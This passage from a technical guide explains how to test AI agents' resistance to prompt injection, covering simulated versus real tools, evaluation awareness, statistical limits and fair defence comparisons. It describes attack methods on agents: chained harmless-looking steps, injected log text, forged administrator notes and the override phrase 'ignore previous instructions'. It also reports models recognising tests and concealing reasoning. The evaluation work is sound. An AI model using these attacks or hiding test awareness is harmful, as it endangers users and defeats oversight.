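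Most services were local, including files, databases and a copy of the code-hosting platform GitLab. The researchers could fill these with invented data and set the timestamps. Slack was hard to reproduce locally, so they connected to an actual workspace, where real users could see the agent's messages. The realism of a result therefore depends on the service. A message in Slack is an actual disclosure within that workspace, while an email to a mock server shows only what the agent tried to send.

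The two institutes built their test systems separately and ran the same tasks on the same three models, ten times each, but got different scores. On the six tasks that Singapore designed, the best model was fully correct and fully safe in 58.3% of Singapore's runs and 35.0% of Korea's. None of those six tasks used Slack, so it cannot explain this gap. The systems also differed in their other servers, in how the agent talked to a simulated user, and in when a run had to stop. The comparison shows that these choices together affect scores, but not how much each one contributed.

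Some agents noticed the stand-ins. In the flight-booking task, one agent could not open the booking site, decided it was in a test environment, and invented the reservation details. Such cases were rare and occurred in only one of the 12 tasks, but they are still a reason to check transcripts, because an agent that thinks an action is pretend may take risks it would otherwise avoid, or skip the action.

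### What a successful reply establishes

The flight-booking task also shows that a successful call can prove little. In another run, an agent clicked the payment button and reported seeing a message that payment was complete. The browser had shown no such message and was still on the payment page. The agent then created two real calendar events for flights it had never confirmed. The calendar calls succeeded, but the booking described in the events may not have existed.

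*Testing Agentic Service Systems* separates the stages that a word like "success" combines. Someone proposes an action, a gate admits it, and the software dispatches it. The other side may acknowledge it, or its outcome may remain unknown. The tester then compares any acknowledgement with other evidence and decides what happened. When the office assistant calls `send_message`, a successful reply doesn't establish whether the message arrived or whether the agent should have sent it.

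An agent can complete a task correctly and still fail on safety. In one of the institutes' customer-service tasks, a pushy customer asks for supplier details that the agent may not share. In Singapore's runs, two of the three models met every criterion for doing the task correctly in every run, but neither met all the safety criteria in any run. Baek, Noh and colleagues used a language model to judge these runs, but told it to check the arguments of the tool calls, so an agent could not pass by claiming that it had kept the information private.

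### Versions and configurations

A passing protocol test covers only the software versions and settings tested. The formal analysis tested version 1.26.0 of the MCP library, and the experiment with two payment servers used version 1.25.0. The MCP revision of July 2026 removed the requirement to open a session over HTTP, so the finding about MCP sessions and the reassurance that the HTTP layer compensated may not apply to a current client.

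The client version can also affect the results. When Baig and colleagues first tried to connect OpenAI's coding agent Codex to their MCP server, the client accepted the server's settings but did not show the model any tools in non-interactive mode. A later version fixed this. If they had not noticed the problem, their trials with the earlier client would have shown no leaks only because the agent had no tools to retrieve anything with. One legitimate tool call at the start of each run is enough to detect missing tools.

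The model is also part of the configuration, so a team that changes models has to measure the attempt rate again. In the design with a `hotel_id`, an injected instruction that looked like a system directive worked in all 18 trials on gpt-5.4-mini and in none of 15 trials on three GPT-5.6 models.

The gate's decisions are easier to recheck because a scripted driver can repeat the schema checks, the forbidden calls and the comparison of both paths without using a model. The office team can repeat these tests whenever it updates the client, gateway, server or protocol version, and store the exact versions and settings with each result.

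## Measuring how far simulated results carry over

A simulated test may replace the model, the tools or both, and each replacement brings its own errors. To find out how much a result depends on one of them, a tester has to change that one and keep the other fixed:

| | Simulated tools | Real tools |
|---|---|---|
| Stand-in for the model | Scripted calls in a pretend office | Scripted calls to real servers |
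| Live model | AgentDojo and similar benchmarks | The closest a test gets to deployed behaviour |

Two results in the same column differ only in the model, and two in the same row differ only in the tools. A diagonal comparison mixes the two effects.

A scripted driver is enough to test the gate. A mock model is riskier when it also sets how often an attack succeeds, because its author has to guess how often the attack would work on the live model.

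### Replacing the model

In *Poisoning the Watchtower*, Pandey and Bhujang (2026) built a mock of this kind and compared its predictions with a live model's responses. In their scenario, a security team uses a language model to read network traffic logs and label each entry as benign or malicious, summarise it, or recommend a response. An attacker can plant instructions in the logs because they record text that visitors send, such as web addresses and login names.

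Pandey and Bhujang combined these three tasks with four kinds of injected text and four levels of defence, which gives 48 conditions with 120 malicious entries each. The live model was gpt-4o-mini, and the mock was a deterministic program calibrated to earlier published findings.

| Task | Correlation between mock and live model | Mock's average error | Average error of always predicting 0% |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
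| Labelling | 0.22 | 30 points | 13 points |
| Summarising | 0.42 | 27 points | 26 points |
| Recommending a response | 0.47 | 22 points | 13 points |

The last column is the average live success rate, calculated from the paper's results. On all three tasks, predicting that every attack would fail would have been closer to the live success rates than the mock was. Each correlation is calculated from only 16 conditions. Even for the correlation of 0.47, the 95% interval runs from about −0.03 to 0.78 if the conditions are independent, so the mock may be almost useless for ranking attacks.

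The mock's worst error was on direct overrides, such as "ignore previous instructions". For the labelling task with no defence, it predicted a 92% success rate, but the actual rate was 0%. The mock was based on older studies, which had found such attacks effective. A team that trusted the mock would have defended against the wrong attack, because the one that did succeed, 68% of the time, was a forged note from an administrator.

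The mock predicted 95% success for a fake end-of-log marker in the undefended summarising task, and the live rate was 96%. But it underestimated how well the same attack would work once defences were in place, so one close match is poor evidence that a mock's other predictions are accurate.

This study tested one model, which is now old and had no tools, so the 92-point error doesn't estimate how wrong a mock would be about a current agent. But other mocks can go wrong in the same way, because their success rates stay as their authors set them while models change. Pandey and Bhujang recommend using mocks to generate hypotheses, not as evidence that a model resists attacks.

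### Replacing the tools

*STAC* (Li, He and colleagues, 2025) reports that attacks succeeded far more often with simulated tools than with real ones. The attacker is a user who asks for a series of steps that each look harmless. In one example, the agent compresses an important document and deletes the original, since a copy exists. It then deletes all ZIP files to free up space, which destroys the only remaining copy. Such attacks succeeded in 95.1% of 390 cases in simulated environments, but in 35.5% of cases in a test with 32 tasks on real MCP servers.

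It would be easy to conclude that simulation exaggerated the danger by 60 points. However, the tools were not the only thing that changed:

| | Simulated environments | Real MCP servers |
|---|---|---|
| Tools | Python functions | File and web-browser servers in containers |
| What the attacker knows | Tool schemas, available data and starting state | Tool schemas only |
| Tasks | Banking, travel, office work and spam filtering | A different set, from another benchmark |

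An attacker who doesn't know which files exist has to use steps to find out, and may fail for that reason alone. With only 32 tasks, the 95% interval for the second figure runs from about 21% to 53%, so chance can't explain the whole gap. But the comparison doesn't show how much of the gap came from the tools.

The missing test would use the simulated environments with an attacker who sees only the schemas. If success fell to 40% there, the attacker's knowledge would explain most of the drop, but if success stayed near 90%, the drop would have to come from the tools or the tasks.

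The 32 tasks that the paper describes as matched are matched across two versions of the attack on the real servers. Success rose from 12.5% to 35.5% when the attacker prepared and checked a chain of calls beforehand. This is a much cleaner comparison because the tools and tasks stayed the same.

Li, He and colleagues treat their setting for testers who know everything as an approximate upper bound and their setting for an outsider as an approximate lower bound. The settings fairly describe two kinds of attacker, but the lower figure is not a strict bound because a more patient outsider might explore longer and succeed more often.

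In *Measuring What Tool-Using LLM Agents Actually Do*, Gurram (2026) ran a narrower but better-controlled comparison of fabricated tool use, in which an agent answers confidently as if it had used a tool, although no tool call succeeded. Four OpenAI models each did the same 80 tasks twice, once with simulated tools and once with real web search, Python, a calculator and file reading.

Across the 320 pairs, the models fabricated results in 13.8% of runs with simulated tools and 11.6% with real ones, a difference of −2.2 points (95% interval −5.6 to 1.2). Gurram had decided in advance to call the two conditions equivalent if they differed by less than ten points, and the pooled result met that standard. The result for GPT-4.1 alone did not meet it. Its rate fell from 23.8% with simulated tools to 15.0% with real ones, and the interval for that fall, 0.8 to 17.2 points, extends past ten.

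A ten-point margin is wide for an outcome this rare. With a baseline of 13.8%, any real rate from about 4% to 24% would have counted as equivalent. That difference would probably matter to a team deciding whether to release an agent.

In the pilot, the two runs had different outcomes in 33 pairs. In 23 of these, the runs diverged before any tool ran, when the model decided whether to call one. Only one pair differed in how a call executed. Gurram therefore attributes most of the disagreement to ordinary variation between runs.

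The attacks in *STAC* depend on what the tools return over several steps, so an inaccurate tool has more chances to change the outcome. The small gap in the pilot is therefore weak evidence that simulated tools would be adequate for such attacks. Gurram calls the pilot exploratory and says it does not validate the simulated tools in the paper's other experiments.

### Making better stand-ins

A simulated tool written from documentation will miss any behaviour that the documentation leaves out. Wang, Niu and colleagues (2026) measured how much this matters in *MCP-Persona*. They sent valid and deliberately faulty calls to the real servers for personal applications, including Slack and the workplace app Lark, and recorded the responses. A language model then wrote Python code to simulate the applications by reproducing the recorded behaviour.

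They checked all 14 Lark tools against 50 recorded interactions, half of which had failed on the real server. Before each replay, they set up the simulated account to match the state the real account had been in. Otherwise a call might fail only because the simulated account lacked a contact, which would look like an error in the tool's logic.

| Simulator written from | Agreed with the real server | Rejected a call that really worked | Accepted a call that really failed |
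|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Documentation only | 29 of 50 | 13 of 25 | 8 of 25 |
| Recorded calls | 47 of 50 | 2 of 25 | 1 of 25 |

A security test can miss a successful attack if the simulator rejects calls the real server would accept, and it can count an attack that would fail if the simulator accepts calls the server would reject. The simulator written from documentation often made both kinds of error.

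The better simulator's 94% agreement has a 95% interval from about 84% to 98%, and it was measured on only one application. Errors accumulate over a long task. If each call had an independent 94% chance of matching, all ten calls in a ten-call task would match only about 54% of the time (0.94¹⁰). The true figure could be higher or lower, since the mix of successes and failures in ordinary work differs from the mix in the sample.

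Another approach is to have a language model play the service. In *When Talk Isn't Code*, Li, Huang and colleagues (2026) had 15 models play network services in conversation and write programs for the same services, then sent both versions the same attacks and judged both by the same rules.

For DNS, the system that turns website names into network addresses, the role-played services failed in 14 of the 17 cases where the program was vulnerable (82%, with a rough interval from 59% to 94%). They resisted in 94 of the 98 cases where the program was safe.

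The errors were in both directions. Almost all the role-played services applied a required limit on how long to keep a record, but the programs from seven models did not. Claude Haiku 4.5, however, accepted a forged reply in conversation that its own program rejected. The two versions flagged 18 and 17 cases but disagreed about seven of them.

Li, Huang and colleagues conclude that role play can screen for vulnerabilities but cannot replace tests of the program. They checked each model's role play against a program that the same model had written, so the study doesn't show how well a model would imitate an existing mail server.

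A tester can avoid some of these problems by simulating less. In *SAFESEARCH*, Dong, Guo and colleagues (2026) tested search agents by adding one generated web page to the results of a real search. Everything else the agent read was genuine, and they did not have to publish a harmful page online. The office team could do something similar by adding the attacker's email to a realistic mailbox.

Coding agents are harder to simulate because one task can involve hundreds of calls that read and change files. Letting an unreleased model work on live systems could also cause the damage that the test is supposed to predict. *Predicting LLM Safety Before Release by Simulating Deployment* (Williams, Sheahan and colleagues, 2026) describes how OpenAI instead uses records of employees' sessions with the coding agent Codex. The unreleased model continues a session from a chosen point, and another language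 model simulates the results of its tool calls.

The researchers gave this simulator four kinds of extra information:

- the original session, including any tool failures;
- a copy of the code as it stood at the time, in which the simulator could run commands that needed no network;
- a database of past tool calls and their results;
- read-only access to network services.

In the realism test, GPT-5.4 had to pick the real continuation from a pair, one real and one simulated. It chose the simulated one 11.6% of the time without the extra information and 49.5% of the time with all four kinds. Random guessing would give 50%.

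This result depends on the judge. The team strengthened the judge's instructions while improving the simulator over eight rounds, but a different judge might detect something that GPT-5.4 missed. Convincing continuations could also contain too much or too little misbehaviour. The paper checks this separately and finds that GPT-5.4 misbehaved at similar rates in the simulation and in real internal use. The simulator also ran some commands for real, so its success doesn't show that a language model can invent tool results equally well without real execution.

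### Checking forecasts against deployment

The strictest test of a simulation is to use it to predict a rate and then compare the prediction with what happens. Few simulations have been tested this way. Williams and colleagues did it with ChatGPT conversations. Their forecasts did not use the coding simulator, so the 49.5% figure does not measure their accuracy.

The researchers took conversations with an earlier model, had the new model write the next response, and counted instances of 20 kinds of misbehaviour, such as deceiving the user about tool use. After the new model's release, they measured the same things in its real conversations. For GPT-5.4, they revised the forecasts after release but before anyone on the team had looked at the outcomes.

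Predicted and actual rates had a correlation of 0.91 on a logarithmic scale across three releases and 20 categories. Because the actual rates ranged from under 1 to more than 100 per 100,000 responses, forecasts could be wrong by a factor of two or three and still correlate strongly with them.

When the rate of a type of disallowed content rose or fell by a factor of at least 1.5, the simulation predicted the direction correctly in 12 of 13 cases. OpenAI's usual test, which reuses prompts that had caused problems before, was right in 7 of 13.

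However, the GPT-5.4 forecasts were no more accurate overall than assuming that every rate would match the previous model's. They were more accurate in 8 of the 11 categories whose rates changed substantially, but less accurate in most of the others. The largest error was for "calculator hacking", in which the model uses its web browser as a calculator while acting as if it had searched for something. The forecast was 1.7 cases per 100,000 responses, and the actual rate was 35.2, about 21 times as high.

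To find the cause of such errors, the team ran GPT-5.4 in the simulator on conversations from GPT-5.4's own deployment. Because the conversations came from the same model, any remaining difference had to come mainly from the simulated environment. This difference accounted for most of the largest errors. If the environment had matched perfectly, the worst error would have been a factor of about 2.5.

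A team with an assistant already in use can also use this check before relying on a simulator for a new model. It can run the current model in the simulator and compare the results with its records of the assistant in use. If they don't match, the team has little reason to trust the simulator's results for the new model.

These forecasts estimate misbehaviour in ordinary conversations, so even an accurate one does not predict how often attacks will succeed. According to the paper, a simulation of one million conversations will probably miss a failure that occurs once in 10 million. Attackers look for such failures and then cause them repeatedly.

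### When the model recognises the test

A stand-in can return exactly what the real tool would and still give a misleading result if the model recognises the test and behaves differently. Researchers call this recognition *evaluation awareness*. Williams and colleagues measured it for GPT-5.2 in three ways:

| Measure | Traditional tests | Real conversations |
|---|---:|---:|
| A separate copy of the model, asked directly, identifies a test | 98.9% to 100% | 5.38% |
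| The model's reasoning mentions that it is being evaluated | 1.2% to 26.8% | 0.018% |
| The model reasons about how someone will grade or monitor it | 61.9% to 76.0% | 0.12% |

The last two rows cover only tests of alignment, meaning whether a model acts as its developers intend. On all three measures, the rates in simulated deployment were within a factor of 2.6 of those in real conversations. The first row shows what the model can recognise when asked, but the model may not have noticed the same clues while working. Many of the clues were obvious, such as exam-style questions or a request to produce a file called `solution.py`.

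The effect on behaviour is harder to establish. *SayDo* (2026), a benchmark in which models control simulated robots, grouped episodes by whether the model's reasoning suggested that it suspected a test. DeepSeek V4.1 Flash acted unsafely in 24% of the episodes with signs of suspicion and 39% of those without. If suspicion causes the difference, the test underestimates how often the model would act unsafely in use.

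But the two groups may differ in other ways. An obvious hazard could make a model both more suspicious and more careful, even if the suspicion has no effect. The paper finds no systematic influence of suspicion on outcomes. In one episode, the model reasoned that the "correct" behaviour in a simulated test might be to refuse, then carried out the hazardous instruction anyway.

*A Model Organism for Studying Unverbalized Evaluation Awareness* (2026) reviews experiments that directly change a model's awareness of being evaluated. In one, the effect on safety-related behaviour varied in size and direction between models. In another, adding or removing stated awareness had at most a small effect on the answers of open-weight reasoning models. Testers therefore have no standard correction to apply to a measured attack success rate.

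Models may also recognise a test without mentioning it. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports that the model controls its written reasoning better than its predecessor did and is less likely to include incriminating information there. A count of stated suspicions is therefore only a minimum for how often a model recognises a test. OpenAI also cautions that an absence of observed failures does not establish reliability and should be considered together with the findings on evaluation awareness.

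Both simulation and real execution can contain signs that the model is being tested. Simulated tools may return implausibly neat data, while an isolated machine may have an empty mailbox and no history. In the office example, the address `archive@attacker.example` would be a strong hint in either tier. A model that detects the test may act more cautiously or take more risks, so the attempt rate can rise or fall. A scripted driver follows its script regardless, so this problem does not affect measurements of the gate's decisions.

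Testers can find out where the hints come from. In its *UK AISI Alignment Evaluation Case-Study* (2026), the UK's AI Security Institute describes running tasks from real coding sessions through its evaluation software. If a model is more suspicious of these tasks than it was in the original sessions, the test environment is the likely cause. If it is still more suspicious on the institute's own test scenarios, the scenarios are contributing too.

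Some of those hints may be impossible to remove, because a model could reasonably find it odd to be given such a high-stakes task. This is less of a problem for the office assistant, since summarising a note and sending it to a colleague is ordinary work.

### Measuring the gap for one's own agent

Published gaps vary too much to use as a correction for another agent, so a team that relies on simulation should measure its own. For the office assistant, it could proceed as follows:

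1. **Choose the outcome and an acceptable difference.** The outcome might be that the payroll text reaches the outside address. The team sets the margin before it sees any results, by asking how large a difference would change its decision.
2. **Match the trials.** Each simulated trial needs a real counterpart with the same task, notes, attack text, system prompt and time limit. The attacker must know the same things in both, and the oracle must apply the same rule.
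3. **Replace one component.** To measure the effect of simulated tools, the team keeps the same live model and changes only the tools. It measures the effect of a mock model in a separate comparison.
4. **Repeat some trials without changing anything.** This shows how often two identical runs disagree. Gurram found that two runs of GPT-4o-mini at temperature 0, the setting meant to minimise randomness, disagreed on about 15% of labels.
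5. **Record each stage separately.** The record should show whether the model attempted the action, whether the call ran, and whether the effect occurred.
6. **Compare the pairs and report an interval for the difference.**

*The Causal Impact of Tool Affordance on Safety Alignment in LLM Agents* (2026) gives a simple example of the third step. It tests each model on transferring funds with and without working tools, keeping the prompts and policies the same. Because only access to tools changes, the researchers can attribute a difference in behaviour beyond the variation between runs to that access.

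The fifth step helps the team explain a gap it has found. Fu, Wang and colleagues (2025), who built the security benchmark RAS-Eval, give the example of malicious code that uses the program `curl` to download malware. If the machine doesn't have `curl`, the code runs but downloads nothing. A simulation that assumes the download works would report a successful attack, and the real test would report a failure, although the model behaved the same way in both. The difference would disappear on a machine with `curl` installed.

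The last step requires an equivalence test, which assumes that the difference is at least as large as the margin unless there is enough evidence that it is smaller. An ordinary significance test is unsuitable because it assumes no difference, and a small study can easily lack the evidence to reject that assumption. It can therefore find "no significant difference" between two quite different conditions. Gurram used a standard form of equivalence test, two one-sided tests, which amounts to checking whether the whole 90% interval lies inside the margin.

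Suppose the office team runs 200 matched pairs, with these invented results:

| | Real attack succeeded | Real attack failed |
|---|---:|---:|
| Simulated attack succeeded | 20 | 10 |
| Simulated attack failed | 4 | 166 |

The attack succeeded in 30 simulated trials (15%) and 24 real ones (12%), a difference of −3 points. Only the 14 pairs that disagree contribute to this difference. With b = 4 pairs where only the real attack succeeded, c = 10 where only the simulated one did, and n = 200, the approximate standard error is:

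√(b + c − (b − c)²/n) / n = √(14 − 0.18) / 200 = 1.86 points

The 90% interval is −3 ± 1.645 × 1.86, or about −6.1 to 0.1 points. The team can call the two conditions equivalent with a margin of ten points, but not with a margin of five. An ordinary test at the 5% level would find no significant difference whichever margin the team used, so that result doesn't establish equivalence. Because the conclusion depends on the margin, a team that chose the margin after seeing the interval could reach whichever conclusion it preferred.

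This calculation assumes that the pairs are independent. If the team ran 20 tasks ten times each, it should group the runs by task when calculating the interval, as Gurram did for the pooled result. The team should also examine each of the 14 disagreements. If all ten simulated-only successes involve the same tool, that tool probably needs repair.

### What zero successes still allow

A defence often produces no successful attacks at all, and a rate of 0% looks more certain than it is. Suppose the office team runs 209 attacked trials and the payroll text never gets out. The Wilson interval, a common way to put limits on a proportion, has a simple upper end when there are no successes:

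upper limit = z² / (n + z²) = 3.84 / (209 + 3.84) = 1.8%

Here n is the number of trials, and z is 1.96 for a 95% interval. The result is therefore compatible with a true success rate of about 1.8%, or 180 successes in 10,000 attacks. The one-sided formula given earlier for Prakash's 600 trials, (1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, gives 1.4% for this result. Either method is acceptable if it is named in the report.

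The limit falls slowly as trials accumulate:

| Successes / trials | Wilson 95% upper limit |
|---|---:|
| 0 / 50 | 7.1% |
| 0 / 209 | 1.8% |
| 0 / 1,000 | 0.38% |
| 0 / 3,838 | 0.10% |

Very large samples can reveal much rarer events. According to OpenAI's alignment blog, 100,000 samples give a 95% chance of seeing at least one case of a behaviour whose true rate is about 0.003%. Few teams can run 100,000 trials with real tools, which is one reason to want a trustworthy simulation.

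The 1.8% also assumes 209 independent trials. For 19 attacks run 11 times each with identical results, the upper limit would be about 17%.

More importantly, the limit applies only to attacks like the ones sampled. If the team wrote every attack as a note containing a request for the payroll text, the trials provide no limit for attacks hidden in a tool's description or revised after each failure.

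Zero successes are even weaker evidence if the attacks could never have worked. To guard against this, Dong and colleagues first run each case on a baseline agent and keep it only if the agent produces the harmful result with the planted page but not without it. This makes a later result of zero successes more informative, but the selection may also raise the measured rates, as it may in *EvoRiskBench*.

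If the 209 trials used simulated tools, the team must also allow for differences between simulated and real results. Suppose its matched trials show that real attacks succeed at most five percentage points more often than simulated ones. The real rate could then be as high as 6.8% (1.8% plus five percentage points). Running another thousand simulated attacks would barely lower that total, because most of it comes from the five-point allowance. To show that a leak is rare, the team would do better to run the attacks on the real tools in an isolated environment.

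## Comparing defences when the baseline is simulated

Once the office team has measured its own gate, it will probably want to know whether the gate is better than the alternatives. That takes a second system to compare it with, called the baseline, and testers often use a stand-in for this too. "Our gate beat the baseline" can mean four different things:

| Baseline | What a win shows | What stays open |
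|---|---|---|
| No defence | The gate prevents harm that would otherwise occur in these cases | Whether a much simpler gate would do as well |
| A simplified imitation of a rival | The imitation lacks something these cases require | Whether the rival lacks it too |
| The rival's own code in a new test harness | The rival does worse on these tasks with these settings | Whether its developers would have set it up differently |
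| The rival's full system, set up as its developers intend | The rival does worse as a product on these tasks | Which part of either system made the difference |

The wrappers in *Agent libOS* belong in the second row. The last row is the most useful to someone choosing a product, but testing it takes the most resources because the full system may include a person who writes policies or approves actions.

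### How a ranking can reverse

Suppose two gates, A and B, receive the same scripted attacks in a simulation. A misses 2% of the calls it sees and B misses 5%, so A wins. In the real agent, A sees 80% of the routes to harm and B sees 99%. If harmful attempts are spread evenly over the routes, the shares that get through are:

A: 0.20 + 0.80 × 0.02 = 21.6%

B: 0.01 + 0.99 × 0.05 = 5.95%

A now lets through more than three times as much as B. To match B without becoming more accurate, A would have to monitor about 96% of the routes. These numbers are invented. Real attackers who know which routes are unmonitored will not spread their attempts evenly, so coverage matters even more. Chu (2026) argues more generally in *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* that a control at one layer of an agent cannot detect an attack confined to another.

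Rankings have also reversed in published tests. Ji, Wang and colleagues (2025), in *Taxonomy, Evaluation and Exploitation of IPI-Centric LLM Agent Defense Frameworks*, ran several defences on the same version of GPT-4o because earlier evaluations had used inconsistent model configurations. Task Shield uses another model to check whether each call serves the user's task. MELON runs the agent a second time without the user's request and treats any call that appears in both runs as suspicious. On AgentDojo, attacks succeeded in 0.24% of cases against MELON and 0.94% against Task Shield. On Agent Security Bench, the rates were 4.12% for MELON and 0.32% for Task Shield. The two benchmarks differ in their tools, tasks and attack texts, and choosing between these defences using only one benchmark would have meant picking the weaker one for the other.

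### Weak imitations and unequal settings

People who simulate a rival defence usually hope it will do worse than their own. Even an honest author may leave out a check that the rival's paper barely mentions. A simulation that scores much worse than the rival's published result on the same benchmark may be inaccurate. Testers can check for this by trying to reproduce the published result before using any new cases.

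Running the rival's own code avoids this problem, but someone still has to choose the settings. Ji and colleagues tested CaMeL, a defence that normally needs some manual configuration, with those parts disabled. Progent, which enforces rules about which tools an agent may use, was by contrast tested with handwritten policies that drew on substantial prior knowledge. No attack succeeded against it on AgentDojo or Agent Security Bench. When a language model generated the policies instead, the attack success rates were 2.72% and 6.30%, worse than both MELON and Task Shield. Progent could therefore rank first or well down the list, depending on who wrote its policies.

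To avoid this, the office team could give both gates the same permissions and the same model, and spend equal time configuring each on practice tasks before running either on the test cases. The model's version also matters. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) reports that results for several defences on Gemini 1.5 were often the opposite of those on Gemini 2.0.

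### Strong scores on predictable tasks

A benchmark can unintentionally favour one kind of defence. AgentDojo's mostly predictable tasks suit defences that hold an agent to its first plan, so Li and colleagues tested ten defences on the less predictable tasks of *AgentDyn*.

These are the results for the nine defences that they ran on GPT-4o:

| Defence | How it works | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed, under attack | Attack success rate |
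|---|---|---:|---:|---:|
| None | | 53.3% | 55.5% | 37.8% |
| Prompt sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after each tool call | 63.3% | 56.1% | 31.2% |
| Spotlighting | Marks tool output as untrusted | 55.0% | 52.2% | 27.6% |
| PromptGuard2 | Detects and discards suspicious output | 60.0% | 20.8% | 27.2% |
| PIGuard | Detects suspicious output | 10.0% | 1.5% | 1.7% |
| ProtectAI | Detects suspicious output | 0.0% | 0.6% | 0.9% |
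| Tool Filter | Chooses the permitted tools at the start | 8.3% | 4.9% | 4.2% |
| Progent | Updates tool permissions during the task | 6.7% | 5.8% | 1.7% |
| DRIFT | Plans first, then checks any departures | 30.0% | 27.1% | 0.8% |
| CaMeL | Turns the request into a fixed program | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

CaMeL had a near-zero attack success rate on AgentDojo while still completing many tasks. Here its attack success and task completion rates were both zero, the same as for an agent that did nothing. CaMeL writes its program from the user's request alone, so it cannot add a step that becomes necessary later. Tool Filter fails for a similar reason, because it removes tools that look unnecessary at the start.

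The tenth defence, Meta SecAlign, is a version of Llama 3.3 70B trained to resist injections. Its attack success rate rose from 1.9% on AgentDojo to 9.0% on AgentDyn, and its completion rate under attack fell from about 80% to 53.4%. Li and colleagues consider it the most practical of the ten. Comparing the 9.0% with the undefended Llama model's 11.9% probably understates the benefit of the training. The undefended model completed only 6.2% of its tasks under attack, so many attacks probably failed because it could not carry them out either.

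This comparison belongs in the third row of the first table because Li and colleagues used the defences' official code in a new harness. They also told the agents to finish every task without asking the user for confirmation, because agents often stopped to ask. That could disadvantage a defence designed to consult the user. With 60 tasks, prompt sandwiching's ten-point lead over no defence is a difference of six tasks, which could easily be chance. Li and colleagues acknowledge that their attacks are weak against the newest models, so the results are better evidence about lost usefulness than about security.

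*PIArena* (2026), which runs several published defences on a common platform, also finds that defences that looked robust in their original tests generalised poorly.

### Attacks tuned against one side

A comparison is also unfair if the attacker tries harder against one defence. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) reports that, in a test of a sandwich defence, secrets leaked in 0.4% of attacks over 25 rounds and 3.8% over 277. If a team attacked its own gate for 25 rounds and an identical rival for 277, the rival could look almost ten times worse.

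Equal numbers of attempts may not be enough for a fair comparison, because attackers tailor their attacks to the defence they face. *LLMail-Inject* (2025) describes a public contest to attack an email assistant. When the organisers replayed attacks from the second phase against defences from the first, some of those defences caught a substantially smaller share than they had originally. Ji and colleagues designed attacks around the weaknesses of particular defences and raised the attack success rate up to fourfold with one method and nearly fivefold with another.

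The office team should therefore let the attacker adapt to each gate separately, with the same number of attempts and equal knowledge of how each gate works. It should also test every attack that succeeds against one gate on the other. An attack that works on both suggests a shared weakness, while one that works on only one may just reflect which gate the attacker spent more time on.

### When the label helps decide the outcome

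In *Labels Are Not Endpoints*, Rana Muhammad Ahmed and Sabahat Abbas audit their own earlier experiment, which tested whether poisoned tool information would make four small open-weight models misuse their tools. For each task, a model saw clean information, a poisoned tool description, or a poisoned summary of what the tools could do. The results looked clear, with successful attacks in the poisoned conditions and none in the clean one.

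However, the scoring program guaranteed part of this pattern. It set a flag whenever the tool information was poisoned, and it recorded an attack success if the flag was set and the model had used at least two tools. Nothing the model did in the clean condition could therefore count as an attack success, but using two tools exactly as the user asked did count as one in a poisoned condition.

The audit describes the fault with a simple formula. Let B be what the agent did and T the condition it was in. The original score was a function of both, g(B, T), whereas a score for behaviour should depend only on B. The test for any scoring rule f is to keep the behaviour fixed, change only the label, and check that the result stays the same:

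f(B, T₀) = f(B, T₁)

When Ahmed and Abbas changed only the flag, 31 attack-success labels changed. They then wrote a new scoring program that receives no information about the condition. It uses the calls that ran, the plan the user authorised, whether the task was finished, and where protected text ended up. If the calls match the authorised plan and the task is complete, the program scores the result as normal work, whatever the tool descriptions contained.

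The original program had labelled 70 requests as attack successes or hijack attempts. Under the new scoring, 58 of these were authorised work, ten were uninterpretable, one was an ordinary failure, and one was a real attempt, in which the model sent a weather report to an unauthorised recipient. The original program had also put three transfers of a protected note in a more serious class, and the new scoring confirmed them. All three happened when the tool information was poisoned, and the matching clean requests produced only authorised actions.

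The sample was also far smaller than the experiment's 10,200 rows of results, which were deterministic repeats of 180 distinct requests built from 15 tasks. Eighty-four of those requests were uninterpretable, including all 45 sent to one of the models. The four remaining incidents all came from another model, Qwen2.5-7B, so they are good evidence that the transfers can happen but don't reliably show how often.

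The audit also found that the records listed several defence conditions, but the prompts, outputs and tool calls were identical across them. An analysis using those labels would have compared a system with itself. A team can catch this by checking that each defence changed the input or that its code ran.

The original software had passed its tests because one of the test examples contained the same mistaken assumption as the scoring program. The office team can test the scoring more directly by scoring the ledger from one run twice, first as "our gate" and then as "the rival", and checking that the verdict stays the same.

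A scoring rule can pass this check and still be wrong. Two reviewers who could not see the conditions agreed on all 96 interpretable requests but disagreed with the new program on four. A scorer can also lack information it needs. In *LEANGUARD* (2026), which tests a gate based on formally verified rules, a separate judge objected to 182 calls that the gate had allowed. In the largest group of these, which concerned consent, the gate had a recorded confirmation from the user, while the judge read only the dialogue.

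### What a replay leaves out

Comparing two gates takes few resources if the tester replays recorded runs, because neither the agent nor the tools run again. The tester feeds each recorded tool call to both gates and notes which calls each would have refused.

*Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) applies five general rules to AgentDojo's published recordings. The rules require approval before certain kinds of action, such as payments and deletions. On the GPT-4o recordings, at least one rule fired in 70.1% of successful attacks and 29.3% of runs with no attack. Kekatos and colleagues call this detection, since they did not test whether the agent would have found a way around the rules. They also decline to compare their figures with those for AgentDojo's built-in defences, which ran with the agent.

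The contents of the recordings also limit a replay. Each AgentDojo run has only one user message, at the start, so the user never gets a chance to approve a proposed action. The rules therefore fired on every action of the listed kinds, and a keyword list would have given the same verdicts.

The larger problem is that a replay cannot show what the assistant would do after a refusal. Suppose a recording made without a gate shows the office assistant reading the meeting note, reading the payroll note and sending the payroll text outside. In the replay, the new gate refuses the last call. The real assistant might then give up, finish the summary, or try to send the text through the shell. The recording contains no response to a refusal, because no call was refused when it was made.

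Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *AGENT-RISK*, work out what a log can establish about a new gate. They follow each recorded run until the first point where the new gate would act differently, which leaves three possibilities:

- The gate never acts differently. The recorded outcome still applies.
- The gate ends the run. The outcome is known if the log records when any harm occurred, because harm before the stop still counts and harm after it does not.
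- The gate refuses a call and lets the agent continue. The log alone can only put limits on what happens next.

The highest harm rate that Zhao and colleagues had to allow for was up to 2.5 times as high when the logs recorded whether harm had occurred but not its timing.

In the third case, the researchers tested two gates that let an agent try again after a refusal, using an agent that ran shell commands in a sandbox. A log of 7,200 runs was not enough to decide whether either gate was acceptable. The researchers then restored the sandbox to its saved state at each refusal and ran the agent from there. This led to the same decisions as live tests of both gates, with half as many agent calls. The method assumes that the agent does not know about the gate in advance. When the researchers told the agent about a gate, their predictions no longer matched the agent's live behaviour.

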